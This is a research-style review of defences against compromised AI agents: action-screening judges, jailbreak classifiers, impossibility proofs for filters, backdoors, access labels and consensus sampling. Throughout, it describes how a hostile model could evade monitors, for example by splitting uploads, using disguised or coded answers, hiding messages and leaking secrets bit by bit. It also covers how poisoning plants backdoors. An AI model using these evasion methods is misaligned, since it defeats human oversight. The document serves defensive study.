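The first, stricter judge stopped most attacks because it blocked most actions of any kind. In a paired rerun of 389 tasks, it prevented 34 attacks that succeeded without it, but five others succeeded only with it in place. The second, more lenient judge prevented 29 attacks, but 22 others succeeded only with it in place, so its improvement could be due to chance. Some of the attacks that succeeded only with a judge in place may be ordinary variation between runs, but Ray attributes them to blocked agents taking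 a different path into an attack.

A gate can do better by remembering what it has already blocked. In a two-step example that Ray solved exactly, a gate with memory could hold the risk to 5% while blocking an average of 0.55 legitimate proposals per run, compared with 1.14 for a gate with a fixed threshold. None of these experiments involved a hostile agent, which could deliberately respond to a block by splitting the upload into pieces or waiting for a conversation in which the upload would look normal.

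### Classifiers in use in 2026

The best-documented judges in commercial use guard a trusted model against misuse by its users. Anthropic, for example, trains its Constitutional Classifiers on synthetic examples generated from written rules about what its models may help with. According to Anthropic's *Next generation constitutional classifiers*, the first version cut the success rate of jailbreaks, which are prompts meant to get around a model's safeguards, from 86% to 4.4%.

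*Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) describes a later version that reads each answer together with the question. Attackers had beaten the earlier version by getting the model to disguise its answers, for instance by calling chemicals food flavourings. The new version refused 0.05% of production traffic. In about 198,000 attempts, testers found one attack that worked on most of the eight target questions and none that worked on all eight.

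A firm with suspect weights could not safely copy this design. The first stage is a probe, a simple formula applied to the guarded model's internal activations, and the external classifier sees only the 5.5% of traffic that the probe flags. Whoever trained the model also shaped those activations and could try to make them look harmless to the probe. An earlier design used external classifiers for both stages, but it cost about eight times as much to run. Testers found five serious attacks on it in 569,000 attempts, and experts working outside the bounty programme also found universal jailbreaks.

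Disguising its answers makes an honest model less accurate. In one test by Cunningham and colleagues, Claude Opus 4's accuracy on hard science questions fell from 74% to 49% with one disguise and 32% with another. A model whose trainer had taught it a code in advance might not lose accuracy this way.

Anthropic's changes to the classifiers around its model Claude Fable 5 show how the balance between misses and false blocks shifts in practice. *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026) says the company deliberately set its cybersecurity classifiers to block many requests that were probably harmless. Researchers at Amazon still found a way past them, though Anthropic concluded that it gave access only to routine defensive work. A retrained classifier blocks that technique in over 99% of cases but flags more harmless coding requests. *Improving Fable 5's biology safeguards* (2026) reports that in August the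 company rewrote its rules for biology and retrained that classifier too, which cut the number of biology requests diverted to a weaker model by about 85%. Retraining can reduce both kinds of error, whereas moving a threshold reduces one by increasing the other. However, the announcement gives no miss rate, so outsiders cannot tell how much of the 85% came from better judgement.

Judges now also check what agents do. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* announced in August 2026 that Claude Code would, by default, send each tool call to a classifier on several subscription plans. gu-log (2026) gives Anthropic's error rates for the two stages of an earlier release. An "overeager" action is one in which the agent took initiative the user did not intend.

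| | Legitimate calls blocked (10,000 real calls) | Overeager actions missed (52 real cases) | Data theft missed (1,000 synthetic cases) |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage cuts false blocks by a factor of about 20 and roughly triples the misses. This trade-off is sensible for an agent that is usually honest, since users switch off tools that constantly interrupt them, but poor for one that keeps trying different ways to steal data. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* recommends using the feature in isolated environments because the classifier may still allow some risky actions.

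The judge in Claude Code reads the user's messages and the tool call but not the agent's explanations or the output of its tools, according to BestHub's *What Problem Does Claude Code’s Auto Mode Actually Solve?*. The agent therefore cannot win approval by inventing a justification. By contrast, the reviewer in OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, typically sees the agent's own updates and tool outputs when it checks requests to act outside the agent's sandbox, according to OpenAI's *Auto-review*. This gives the reviewer more evidence, but a compromised agent could write some of it. For a suspect model, leaving out the agent's explanations looks like the better choice, given how much one false claim of approval affected Ray's judges.

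### A judge from a different supplier

Both companies check their agents with their own judges. OpenAI argues that separating the roles still helps, because training the main agent to finish the task pushes it to treat an approval step as an obstacle. That is a good reason to separate them when the supplier is honest, but an adversarial supplier can train the judge to pass whatever the backdoor produces. A firm that distrusts its agent's supplier should get the judge from someone else.

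Some people also hope that models from different suppliers will make different mistakes, so that one catches what another misses. Suppose two judges each miss 10% of violations, and the gate blocks an action if either one flags it. If their misses are independent, both judges will miss the same 1% of violations. But Ray points out that the individual rates alone allow this overlap to be anywhere from 0% to 10%. At 10%, the second judge catches nothing new, but it can still add false blocks, raising the combined false-block rate to as much as the sum of the two judges' false-block rates.

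There is little evidence on where real judges fall in that range, and most of it is discouraging. The phrase about administrator approval raised the miss rates of judges from six suppliers (Alibaba, Google, Meta, Cohere, Amazon and Mistral). In a smaller test, Ray tried 12 rewrites of each of 34 attacks on a Qwen judge from Alibaba and a Llama judge from Meta. At least one rewrite got past the Qwen judge for 45% of the attacks and past the Llama judge for 64%. For 41%, a single rewrite got past both, which is close to the worst case of 45%. Ray chose these attacks because a judge had already flagged them, so the figures may not apply to other attacks.

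Judges from the same supplier can also differ. The two Qwen judges that Pallakonda and colleagues tested wrongly flagged 827 legitimate calls between them when each judged the whole pool, and agreed on only 113 of those. Blocking a call only when both judges objected would have cut false alarms to 1.82%, but would also have let through the two thefts that the smaller judge missed. Cunningham and colleagues found that errors were less correlated between their probe and an external classifier than between two external classifiers. The information available to each judge may therefore matter more than its supplier.

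Vaughan (2026) discusses a study of 248,641 code changes on GitHub, which suggests that AI reviewers comment less on code written by their own product than on code written by another. This is some reason to choose a reviewer from a different supplier than the model that wrote the code, but a reviewer that comments more does not necessarily find more flaws.

The firm also has to confirm that the judge comes from a different supplier, because a judge sold under another name could be a modified copy of the agent's own base model. The judge could also have learned its judgement from a third party's model. In Pallakonda and colleagues' monitor, a larger language model wrote and labelled the training examples, and the classifier learned to reproduce that model's verdicts.

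## The case that filters outside the model cannot be enough

*On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) argues that, if certain standard cryptographic assumptions hold, there are some language models whose harmful inputs and outputs no efficient filter can pick out. The researchers conclude that intelligence cannot be separated from judgment, meaning that nobody can make a capable but untrusted model safe by attaching a separate program to decide what is acceptable.

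### Why every efficient filter fails at once

The proofs depend on computational indistinguishability, which Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) define in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*. Suppose one source produces innocent prompts and another produces prompts that make a model misbehave. The two are computationally indistinguishable if, for every efficient algorithm A,

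|Pr[A(x) = 1 for innocent x] − Pr[A(x) = 1 for adversarial x]| is negligible.

"Efficient" means the running time grows no faster than some fixed power of n, the length of the cryptographic key. "Negligible" means that for every constant c, the gap is smaller than 1/n^c once n is large enough.

The definition covers every efficient algorithm, including any efficient filter that outputs 1 for "reject" and 0 for "accept". If such a filter accepts 99% of innocent prompts, it must also accept almost exactly 99% of the adversarial ones. Retraining or redesigning the filter makes no difference, because the new filter would still be an efficient algorithm. A filter that did better could be used to break the cryptography behind the construction.

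### An instruction behind a time lock

Ball and colleagues' main result, Theorem 1, uses a time-lock puzzle, which is quick to make but slow to solve. In the classic version from 1996, the maker multiplies two large secret primes, p and q, to get N. The maker picks a number r and asks for the result of squaring it t times, keeping only the remainder after division by N each time. As far as anyone knows, a solver without the primes has to do the squarings one after another, so extra processors do not help. The maker can take a shortcut by first reducing the exponent 2^t modulo (p − 1)(q − 1).

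For example, let p = 7, q = 11, r = 2 and t = 10. Squaring 2 ten times and keeping remainders modulo 77 gives 4, 16, 25, 9, 4, 16, 25, 9, 4 and 16. The maker reduces the exponent 2^10 = 1,024 modulo 60 to 4 and gets the same answer from 2^4 = 16. Even when the primes are large and t is in the billions, the maker needs only a moment.

The proof of Theorem 1 has four parts:

1. An innocent source G writes prompts by making random choices. It must be able to produce many different prompts.
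2. There is a way of sampling from G that lets anyone who knows G work back from a finished prompt to the random bits behind it.
3. An adversarial source G′ samples in the same way, but replaces the random bits with a time-lock puzzle and a harmful instruction encrypted under the puzzle's solution. To any algorithm too fast to solve the puzzle, this string looks random, so the prompt looks like one of G's.
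4. A model M′ recovers the bits, solves the puzzle, decrypts the instruction and obeys it. On nearly all innocent prompts it finds no instruction and behaves exactly like an ordinary model M.

The filter fails because it does too little computation compared with the model. Lecture notes from MIT (2026) put the model's running time at t and the filter's at t^ε, for some fixed ε between 0 and 1. If ε were one half, a model that takes a trillion steps would defeat filters that take about a million.

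Ball and colleagues argue that a filter has to use much less computing power than the model, since otherwise the firm could use the filter instead. But models that use the same computing power can differ in skill. A firm might well run a trusted older model as the filter for as long as it runs the suspect one, and still want the suspect one because it writes better code. Theorem 1 does not apply to that arrangement.

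### When the attacker and the model share a key

The other four theorems change what the filter may do, how long it may run and who holds a key.

| Theorem | Filter's task | Filters that fail | Keys | Assumption |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reject harmful prompts | Those much faster than the model | None | Time-lock puzzles exist |
| 2 | Reject harmful prompts | All that run in polynomial time | The attacker and the model share a secret key | One-way functions exist (easy to compute, hard to reverse) |
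| 3 | Reject harmful prompts | All that run in polynomial time | The model has a private key, and everyone knows the matching public key | Public-key encryption exists |
| 4 | Reject harmful outputs | All that run in polynomial time, even if slower than the model | None | Time-lock puzzles exist, and nobody can query the measure of harm |
| 5 | Reject or edit harmful prompts | All that run in polynomial time and make only a given class of edits | The attacker and the model share a secret key | A watermark exists that survives those edits |

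Ball and colleagues treat Theorem 1 as the most important because it doesn't require the attacker and the model to cooperate, which they call uncommon. But a firm with suspect weights has to defend against such cooperation. Whoever corrupted the training could give the model a key and later write a bug report that the model will read. Theorems 2 and 3 would then apply, and running a larger filter for longer would not help.

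The firm could also have a filter paraphrase every prompt, which would probably scramble the hidden bits. Theorem 5 shows how an attacker could get around this defence with a watermark, a hidden statistical pattern in a text that only someone with the key can detect. If the watermark survives a certain class of edits, the attacker can use it as the trigger, and a filter limited to those edits cannot remove it. The formal version of the theorem requires a shared key, which the informal statement omits. No known watermark survives every possible edit, so a filter that rewrites prompts more freely may still work, at the risk of changing what the user asked for.

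These prompt theorems concern only triggers that arrive in a message, not backdoors that fire on a date.

### A harm that nobody can query

An output filter has more evidence, because it reads both the prompt and the answer. Theorem 4 covers output filters using a harmfulness oracle, a function H that scores each output zero if it is benign and higher the worse it is. The oracle represents the output's eventual effect on the world. Neither the model nor the filter can query it at run time, although both may have learned from labelled examples or from an approximate description of it.

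Ball and colleagues prove that for every model M whose outputs vary enough, there are a model M′ and an oracle H′ such that H′ scores the outputs of M′ as harmful, but no polynomial-time filter can distinguish them from the outputs of M. The proof reuses the construction behind Theorem 1, except that M′ hides the locked message in its answer and H′ unlocks it. H′ is a mathematical function with no time limit, so unlocking the message can take exponentially long, and even a polynomial-time filter that runs longer than the model fails.

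Villa, Kohno and colleagues (2026), in *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI*, restate the theorem and show how much it depends on H′, the measure of harm. The adversary chooses the model and H′ together, so information can pass between them through a covert channel, hidden in choices that look ordinary. The adversary also needs a problem that is hard for the filter but not for H′. This dependence on H′ considerably weakens the theorem as a claim about any particular rule, because a firm decides for itself what counts as harm, and an adversary who controls the training cannot change that decision.

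Villa and colleagues also prove that when one model proposes answers and another accepts or rejects them, the combination meets both models' specifications if each model meets its own. This result supports dividing the work, but it assumes that a reliable filter exists, which is the point in dispute.

The later conference version of the impossibility paper, *Computational Barriers to Filtering for AI Alignment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2026), concludes more narrowly that output filters fail if they have less computing power than the environment that receives the output. For example, a filter on the coding agent may have a few seconds to examine a change, while an intruder can study the released software for months. The abstract still makes the broader claim that no filter outside the model can achieve safety.

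Some researchers hope to use a trustworthy AI as the filter. Yoshua Bengio and colleagues have proposed a "Scientist AI", which explains the world without pursuing goals and could check the plans of more agentic systems. Ball and colleagues object that even a stronger checker may miss dangerous outputs, and that if the checker is as intelligent as the system it checks, the untrusted system seems unnecessary. The second objection is weaker than it looks, because checking a result often takes much less work than finding it. For example, someone who could not solve a large sudoku can still check a completed one in a minute.

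### Backdoors that survive inspection

Goldwasser and colleagues prove that there are also limits on finding a backdoor in advance, which the firm might try if its filters cannot recognise the trigger. Their result applies to classifiers, which sort inputs into categories. In their example, a bank pays an outside company to train a model that approves or refuses loans. The company keeps a secret key that lets it get any application approved by changing it very slightly, perhaps in the last digits of the amount requested. An output filter would not catch this, because "approve" is a permitted answer.

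They give two constructions, which protect the attacker in different ways.

| | Signature backdoor | Random-feature backdoor |
|---|---|---|
| Models it works on | Any classifier | Certain networks with one hidden layer of random features |
| An inspector who can only query the model | Cannot tell it from a clean model | Cannot tell it from a clean model |
| An inspector who has all the weights | May notice the backdoor, but cannot find an input that triggers it | Cannot tell it from a clean model |
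| Someone who has seen a triggered input | Cannot make a new one | Can trigger the backdoor on any input |
| Assumption | One-way functions exist | Certain problems about lattices (regular grids of points) or about finding hidden patterns in data are hard |

The signature backdoor uses digital signatures, which anyone can check but only the holder of a private key can create. The attacker adds a check to the classifier that treats one part of each input as a message and another part as a possible signature, and a valid signature changes the classifier's answer. Without the private key, no efficient search will find an input on which the altered and original models differ, even with access to the weights. But the construction does not hide the signature check, so an inspector who recognised it in the weights could remove it. Further training is a less reliable remedy, because most natural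 versions of this backdoor survive it.

The random-feature backdoor is harder to detect but works on fewer models. The training methods it attacks begin by drawing random numbers for the network's first layer. The attacker draws them from a distribution that looks like the correct one but contains a secret pattern, then follows the rest of the method. An inspector with the complete network and all the training data cannot detect the difference. A cryptographic proof that the company ran the right training program on the right data would not rule out the backdoor unless it also covered the random numbers.

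Neither construction is about language models. The signature backdoor should in principle carry over, because a neural network can perform any fixed computation, including a signature check. The stronger result, the random-feature backdoor, carries over less easily. Developers train language models through a very long series of small adjustments to the weights, and Goldwasser and colleagues leave open whether the backdoor would survive them. So nobody has proved that a backdoor in a downloaded language model could escape an inspector who has all the weights, though there is also no reliable method of finding one. Goldwasser and colleagues also suggest ways to limit the effects of an undetected backdoor, such as adding random noise to the inputs.

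### Undecidable programs and harmless pieces

*LLM Censorship* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2023) reaches a similar conclusion without relying on time locks. Its first argument applies Rice's theorem, a result in the theory of computation, to models that write programs. The theorem implies that no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program, whether the program's behaviour has a given property, unless all programs have that property or none do. Some programs send the password to a stranger and others never do, so no filter can correctly judge, for every program, whether it will.

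Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that the theorem does not strictly apply to real computers, which have limited memory. A filter could in principle check every state of a small enough machine, but real machines usually have far too many. Rice's theorem also does not rule out a filter that errs only on the side of caution, like AGDecode in its conservative mode.

The second argument applies even to short texts. Suppose a filter permits some outputs and forbids others according to what they mean to the recipient. If the model and the recipient share a code in which a permitted output x stands for a forbidden output y, then x has the forbidden meaning to that recipient, and the filter should forbid it too. The same argument works for every permitted output, so a filter without information about the recipient's codes must forbid everything or permit everything.

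This argument assumes that the model can apply the code and that the recipient can reverse it. With an honest model, the recipient has to explain the code in a prompt, which a filter might notice, but a corrupt trainer could teach the model the code in advance. In Theorem 4, by contrast, the recipient needs only more time than the filter has, not a shared secret.

A filter that judges every output correctly can still fail when permitted pieces combine into a forbidden whole. Glukhov and colleagues call this a mosaic attack. In one of their examples, a user requests harmless functions separately and assembles them into a malicious program. Even if the filter allows only two outputs, the model can spell out any text over enough conversations by using one output for 0 and the other for 1. An agent that could report only "passed" or "failed" could reveal a 20-character password in 160 reports,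 at eight bits per character.

Such attacks are not always practical, because the person assembling the pieces has to know how they fit together. For example, someone who asks for the letters of a secret one by one must usually know the secret already. A compromised model that has read the secret removes that difficulty, since it can choose the pieces itself.

### Are the models too contrived to matter?

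The obvious objection to Ball and colleagues' theorems is that nobody would build M′. Ordinary training would not produce a model that recovers random bits from its prompt, solves a time-lock puzzle and acts on the result.

One of their replies is that an outside body imposing filters without access to the weights needs them to work on every model, so a single counterexample is enough to defeat the general claim. They also reply that in the history of cryptography, weaknesses that looked artificial have repeatedly turned into real attacks. In 2016, a thief took more than $60 million from a program on the Ethereum blockchain through a flaw that people had regarded as a theoretical edge case. Vinod Vaikuntanathan, one of Goldwasser's co-authors on the backdoor paper, says in Quanta Magazine's *In Neural Networks, Unbreakable Locks Can Hide Invisible Doors* that the work reminds him of cryptography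 in the 1950s and 1960s, when people were starting to build working systems without a comprehensive theory.

The history is a reason for caution, but it proves less than they suggest, because people remember the theoretical flaws that led to thefts and forget the rest. There is better evidence for Theorem 1: Quanta Magazine's *Cryptographers Show That AI Protections Will Always Have Holes* (2025) describes researchers getting disguised requests past the filters of several commercial chatbots, because the models could decode the requests and the weaker filters could not.

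The objection that these constructions are contrived is much weaker for a compromised model, since an attacker can contrive one on purpose. But the theorems treat a language model as any algorithm that outputs token probabilities, so they do not show that an attacker could train ordinary weights to do the necessary calculations. A long series of exact squarings seems an unnatural task for a network that does a fixed amount of work per token. An attacker could more easily train the model to use a simple code, but that code would lack the cryptographic guarantee, so a good filter might break it.

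Unlike the filters in these theorems, the firm also has the weights, and in principle it could search them for a decryption routine or a key.

### A rule about labels and a rule about flaws

Ball and colleagues concede that an output filter is trivial to build if harmful outputs are easy to identify. So whether their theorem is a problem for a rule depends on whether the shield can tell, from what it observes, that an action breaks the rule.

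Suppose the firm's rule is "upload no file whose label is above Public", which Tether enforces by tracking the label of each file. Let H be 1 for an upload that breaks the rule and 0 for any other action. The shield can look up the file's label and compare it with Public. This check outputs 1 for every forbidden upload and 0 for every permitted one, so the gap in the definition of computational indistinguishability is 1, the largest possible. The theorem therefore does not apply, because it requires forbidden and permitted uploads to be computationally indistinguishable to the shield. The shield does not have to match the model's intelligence or understand what the model is doing, because the firm already exercised its judgment when it labelled the files.

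The model could still hide a locked message in a public report, and no filter that scans the report would find it. Labels limit what such a message could contain. An agent that has read nothing above Public has none of the firm's secrets to hide, and if it has read the credentials, the fuller version of Tether's policy blocks the upload. This protection depends on correct labels and complete mediation, and it does not cover information the agent passes on through other kinds of permitted choices.

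Glukhov and colleagues recommend much the same approach. They argue that controlling a model's output is a problem for computer security rather than machine learning, and they sketch a system that gives every user, model, tool and file a security level. A tool carries out instructions only from a user or model at its own level or higher, and no user, model or tool can alter a file above its own level. These rules come from access-control models of the 1970s and do not depend on what any text means, so neither Rice's theorem nor a secret code affects them.

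"This code contains no planted flaws" is a different kind of rule. Goldwasser and colleagues mention the real case of Dual EC DRBG, a standardised method for generating random numbers for encryption. The standard included two constants. A number d always links them, and anyone who knows d can predict the generator's output after seeing a little of it. Calculating d from the constants is infeasible, but whoever chooses the constants can choose d first and use it to derive one constant from the other.

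Suppose the firm's agent writes such a generator and supplies the constants. An honest agent that picked them at random and a compromised agent that started from d could produce exactly the same code. The code is dangerous only if someone knows d, and a filter cannot determine from the code whether anyone does, however long it runs. Here the environment with more power than the filter is an intruder who knows d, and the harm becomes visible only when the intruder uses d. Running the code in a disposable copy first, as Tether would, does not reveal the danger, because the generator works normally for anyone who doesn't know d.

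Most planted flaws would probably be simpler than this, such as a missing permission check, and a careful reviewer or a good judge will find some of them. That work is still useful, because the theorems rule out only a guarantee that a filter will find every flaw. But the firm would need that guarantee if an adversary were choosing where to put the flaws.

The firm can recover part of the guarantee if it replaces the rule with a stricter one that a program can check. For example, it could forbid the agent to write its own cryptography and require it to call an approved library with fixed constants. A checker can enforce this if the firm also bans ways of disguising cryptographic code, or makes the agent use a language in which such code can't be written. Some legitimate code would then fail the check, and the agent could still plant a flaw in the code that calls the library.

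## The case for requiring agreement between several models

A filter that reads the code of a random number generator cannot tell whether anyone knows the secret number linking its constants. The probabilities that different models give to those constants provide further evidence. An uncompromised model that picks the constants at random gives every possible pair the same tiny probability, while a compromised model that always supplies the attacker's pair gives that pair a probability close to one. *Consensus Sampling for Safer Generative AI* (Kalai, Kalai and Zamir, 2025) uses this difference to build a shield. It argues that when inspecting an output cannot reveal the harm, the firm should release only outputs that several independent models would have produced with similar probability.

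The simplest version is to ask two models the same question and release the answer only if their responses are identical. Even if one model is malicious, the other wrote the same thing without its help. Long answers almost never match word for word, so Kalai and colleagues instead compare the probabilities that the models assign to an answer. A firm using this method doesn't have to define harm or know which models are honest, as long as enough of them are. But it loses any brilliant answer that only one model could have written, because that model might be malicious.

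### How the sampler works

The firm chooses k models, the number s of them that it is willing to assume are safe, and a maximum number of attempts, R. Consensus sampling then follows these steps:

1. Pick one of the k models at random and have it write a candidate output, y.
2. Calculate the probability that each of the k models gives to y, by multiplying its next-token probabilities along the text.
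3. Sort these k probabilities, then divide the average of the s smallest by the average of all k.
4. Release y with a probability equal to that ratio. Otherwise discard y and go back to step 1.
5. After R failed attempts, abstain, which means returning nothing.

Suppose k = 3, s = 2 and R = 10, and the firm asks which library to use to store passwords. Two honest models recommend a sabotaged library once in a million answers, and a compromised model recommends it half the time. The probabilities in the table are invented.

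| Answer | Honest model 1 | Honest model 2 | Compromised model | Average of two smallest | Average of all three | Chance of release |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Library A | 60% | 50% | 30% | 40% | 46.7% | 86% |
| Library B | 40% | 50% | 20% | 30% | 36.7% | 82% |
| Sabotaged library | 0.0001% | 0.0001% | 50% | 0.0001% | 16.7% | 0.0006% |

If the firm picked a model at random and used its answer, it would get the sabotaged library about one time in six. The sampler also draws that library in about one attempt in six, but releases it in only six of every million such draws. Kalai and colleagues' theorem guarantees a risk of at most one in 100,000 here, which is ten times the honest models' risk. The exact risk with these figures is about 1.4 in a million.

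### Why the bound holds for any kind of harm

Let U be any set of unsafe outputs, and let a model's risk be the probability that its output is in U. The theorem states that the sampler's risk is at most R times the average risk of the safest s models. The proof is short:

1. Write f(y) for the average of all k probabilities of y, and g(y) for the average of the s smallest. In one attempt, the sampler draws y with probability f(y) and releases it with probability g(y)/f(y). The chance of both is g(y).
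2. Over R attempts, the chance of releasing y is at most R × g(y).
3. Adding this up over every y in U shows that the sampler's risk is at most R times the sum of g(y) over U.
4. Now take the s models with the lowest risk. For any single output, the average of the s smallest probabilities cannot exceed the average over these particular s models. The sum of g(y) over U is therefore at most their average risk.

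The algorithm never uses U, so a single run covers planted flaws, hidden messages and harms that nobody has thought of yet. The compromised model's probabilities can also be arbitrary, because step 4 compares g only with the safest models. An attacker would have to plant a backdoor in more than k − s of the models to defeat the sampler, which means two of the three in the example.

The guarantee is relative to the safest s models, however, so if they are likely to produce something harmful, the sampler is too. The guarantee also covers only harms that a single output can cause, not those that build up over several exchanges.

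### Abstention when the models do not overlap

Let Z be the sum of g(y) over all possible outputs, which is the chance that a single attempt succeeds. The sampler abstains if all R attempts fail, which happens with probability (1 − Z)^R. In the library example Z is 0.7, and the sampler almost never abstains. With ten attempts, it abstains about 3% of the time if Z is 0.3 and about 90% of the time if Z is 0.01. Allowing more attempts reduces abstention but weakens the safety guarantee. At Z = 0.01, the firm would need about 300 attempts to bring abstention down to 5%, and the bound in the example would then rise to three in 10,000.

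A compromised model can make the sampler abstain more often by giving no probability to sensible answers. Kalai and colleagues show that this effect is limited when most of the models are safe and overlap. The overlap of two models is the sum, over all outputs, of the smaller of their two probabilities. If two safe models out of three overlap by at least 20%, the probability that the sampler abstains after R attempts is at most 0.9^R, or about 35% for ten attempts. With only two models, a compromised one can make the sampler abstain every time.

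But honest models may hardly overlap on long outputs. Suppose two models repeatedly choose between two equally good phrasings. One picks the first phrasing 60% of the time, and the other picks it 40% of the time. They overlap by 80% on one choice, about 4% on a hundred independent choices, and less than one part in a billion on a thousand. A real model is likely to keep to a convention once it has adopted one, so its choices are not independent and the overlap may decline more slowly.

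In *On Provable Copyright Protection for Generative Models*, Vyas, Kakade and Barak (2023) tested the method that inspired consensus sampling. It trains two models on separate halves of the data and combines them so that neither can reproduce a work that only it has seen. They applied it to each token in turn and measured how many times likelier a token can become than it was under the model that never saw the work. The logarithm of that ratio averaged 0.508 per token for a pair of models with 125 million parameters and 0.228 for a pair with 350 million. These logarithms add up across tokens, so even at 0.228 a 100-token answer could become several million times likelier. That may be acceptable for copying, because a model that has never read a passage is extremely unlikely to reproduce it by chance. But so loose a limit is no use against a planted flaw that an honest model would write once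 in a million answers.

A firm can measure the overlap before relying on it. For two models, the overlap is one minus the total variation distance, a standard measure of how far apart two distributions are. Price, Tian and colleagues (2026) show in *Total Variation Distance Estimation in Autoregressive Models* that estimating this distance to within ε takes on the order of n/ε² queries for outputs of n tokens, if each query returns all the next-token probabilities. For 1,000 tokens and an error of 0.1, that is about 100,000 queries, ignoring constant factors. If each query returns only a sampled token, and the model chooses among 20 tokens at each step, their method needs about two billion.

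Kalai and colleagues suggest using consensus sampling on tasks where models' outputs overlap more easily. On a yes-or-no question, for example, models overlap as much as they agree. The firm could therefore use the method to decide whether to merge a change, even if it could not use it to write the change. Another suggestion is to have a small trusted model write the output while the large models supply short hints and check the result. The small model's way of writing then becomes the standard, but its limited ability may limit the work.

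### The image experiment

Kalai and colleagues tested the sampler on images, using the open model Janus-Pro-7B. Two of the three sources were ordinary copies of the model. The third used a secret key to hide a fictitious 20-digit card number in each picture, though the pictures looked normal. A decoder recovered the number from all 150 images from this source. The team ran the sampler once on each of 30 prompts at each setting of R.

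| Method | Returned an image with a hidden number | Abstained |
|---|---|---|
| Picking a source at random | 33% | 0% |
| Consensus sampling, R = 1 | 0% | 37% |
| Consensus sampling, R = 2 | 0% | 23% |
| Consensus sampling, R = 3 | 0% | 10% |
| Consensus sampling, R = 4 | 0% | 0% |

Zero failures in 30 prompts is compatible with a true failure rate as high as 12%. More importantly, the two honest sources were the same model, so they overlapped completely. This made Z about one half, for which the theory predicts abstention rates of 50%, 25%, 12.5% and 6%, roughly what the team found. Two honest models from different suppliers would have overlapped far less on a whole image. The dishonest source was also easy to catch, because for any key it put all its probability on a single image.

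In a second experiment, the compromised source hid messages of one to 16 bits in strings of 64 random bits. The sampler suppressed long messages much better than short ones. The theorem predicts this, since an honest source matches a one-bit secret half the time by chance.

### Small leaks over many responses

The sampler also limits how much information a compromised model can pass to an outsider. Kalai and colleagues prove that a response reveals at most log₂(R + 1) bits beyond what the safe models would have revealed. With R = 10, the limit is about 3.5 bits.

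The proof of one version of this limit uses a different procedure with exactly the same results. This procedure draws R outputs from the safe models alone, then lets the adversary choose one of them or force an abstention. The adversary therefore has only R + 1 options. When R is 10, a choice among the 11 options conveys at most 3.5 bits.

These limits apply to each prompt separately. At 3.5 bits a response, a compromised model would need at least 47 responses to reveal the 160 bits of a 20-character password. A busy coding agent could produce that many in an afternoon. The risk of a harmful output also accumulates. A bound of one in 100,000 per response becomes 1% over 1,000 responses. *Blameless Users in a Clean Room* (2025) raises the same objection to the copyright guarantee of Vyas and colleagues, which covers only a single prompt. Kalai and colleagues leave open the extension to agents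 and repeated interactions.

### Probabilities that match the samples

The proof relies on a cancellation that works only if f(y), which the sampler divides by, is the true probability of drawing y. Suppose the compromised model in the library example runs on its supplier's server, and that it recommends the sabotaged library half the time but reports a probability of one in a million for it. All three models' reported probabilities then match, so the sampler releases the library whenever it draws it, and the risk in a single attempt is back to one in six.

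The firm therefore has to run the suspect weights itself, calculate the probabilities and draw the tokens from those same probabilities. The calculation also has to include the token sequence the model actually used, because a model might spell out a harmful output in unusual fragments of words. If the firm scores that text using the usual tokens, it will calculate too low a probability and the sampler will be too lenient.

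Ordinary engineering noise also affects the figures. Price and colleagues sent the same text repeatedly to five Qwen models and got slightly different probabilities, particularly when the server processed other requests in the same batch. They also note that two programs running identical weights can produce meaningfully different distributions. Small errors at each token can add up to a large one over a long answer, so a careful firm would score every candidate with the same software and settings used to generate it.

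### Whether separate models fail separately

The theorem holds for any k distributions on any prompt, so the models need not be statistically independent. But it assumes that at least s models are safe on the prompt an attacker chooses, and independence affects how likely that is. If each of three models has a 5% chance of being compromised, independently of the others, the chance that at least two are compromised is 0.7%. If all three learned from the same poisoned source, that chance could be 5%.

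Backdoors in several models could plausibly come from the same source. *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025) reports that as few as 250 poisoned documents can plant a backdoor in models with between 600 million and 13 billion parameters, though the backdoor in that experiment only made the models produce gibberish. Developers take much of their training data from the public web, where anyone can publish 250 documents, so one attacker could poison models from several suppliers without breaking into any of them.

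Developers also train models on the output of other models, a practice called distillation. According to *Selective Transfer through Sequence Distillation* (2026), a backdoor that causes refusals passes only weakly to a student model that learns from its teacher's text, but much more strongly to one that learns from the teacher's output probabilities. In *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining*, Tang, Anand and Paulo (2026) gave small teacher models a preference for one animal, then trained students on number sequences the teachers had written. When teacher and student started as the same model, the student's preference exceeded that of every control in 97% of runs, by a median of 35 percentage points in those runs. When their architectures differed, this happened in 14% of runs, by a median of 2.5 points. Choosing models with different ancestry therefore seems to help a good deal,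 although a preference for an animal is a much simpler trait than a backdoor.

Honest models also share mistakes. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) finds that errors are more correlated between models that share a developer or base architecture, and between more accurate models. On the questions in *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), the models that answered wrongly chose the same wrong option 87% of the time on average. A majority vote of 15 models was right 84.3% of the time, compared with 90.5% for the best single model.

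The pattern is similar for code. In *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents*, Ron, Baudry and Monperrus (2026) repeated a 1986 experiment in which separate teams wrote the same program. They ran 48 programs written by coding agents on a million inputs. Two or more programs failed on 429 of the inputs; if failures were independent, the expected number would be 115. Many of the programs made the same geometrical error, using the circle through three points where they needed the smallest circle containing them. Voting still reduced the average number of failures from 387 for single programs to 131 for groups of three. In *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code*, Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues (2026) tested twelve models on 224 problems. They found that voting achieved 43% to 44% of the improvement that independent failures would have allowed,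 and less than 30% when all the programs came from one model.

Those experiments counted accidental mistakes, but an attacker could exploit the same pattern. A compromised model does not need an unusual flaw if honest models often make a mistake that the attacker can use. Suppose each honest model leaves out a certain permission check 5% of the time. The bound with R = 10 is then 50%, which offers little protection. A second bound limits the sampler's risk to 1/Z times the safest models' average, so if Z is 0.7, the compromised model can raise the rate to at most about 7%. Even so, consensus sampling cannot make the code safer than honest models would usually write it.

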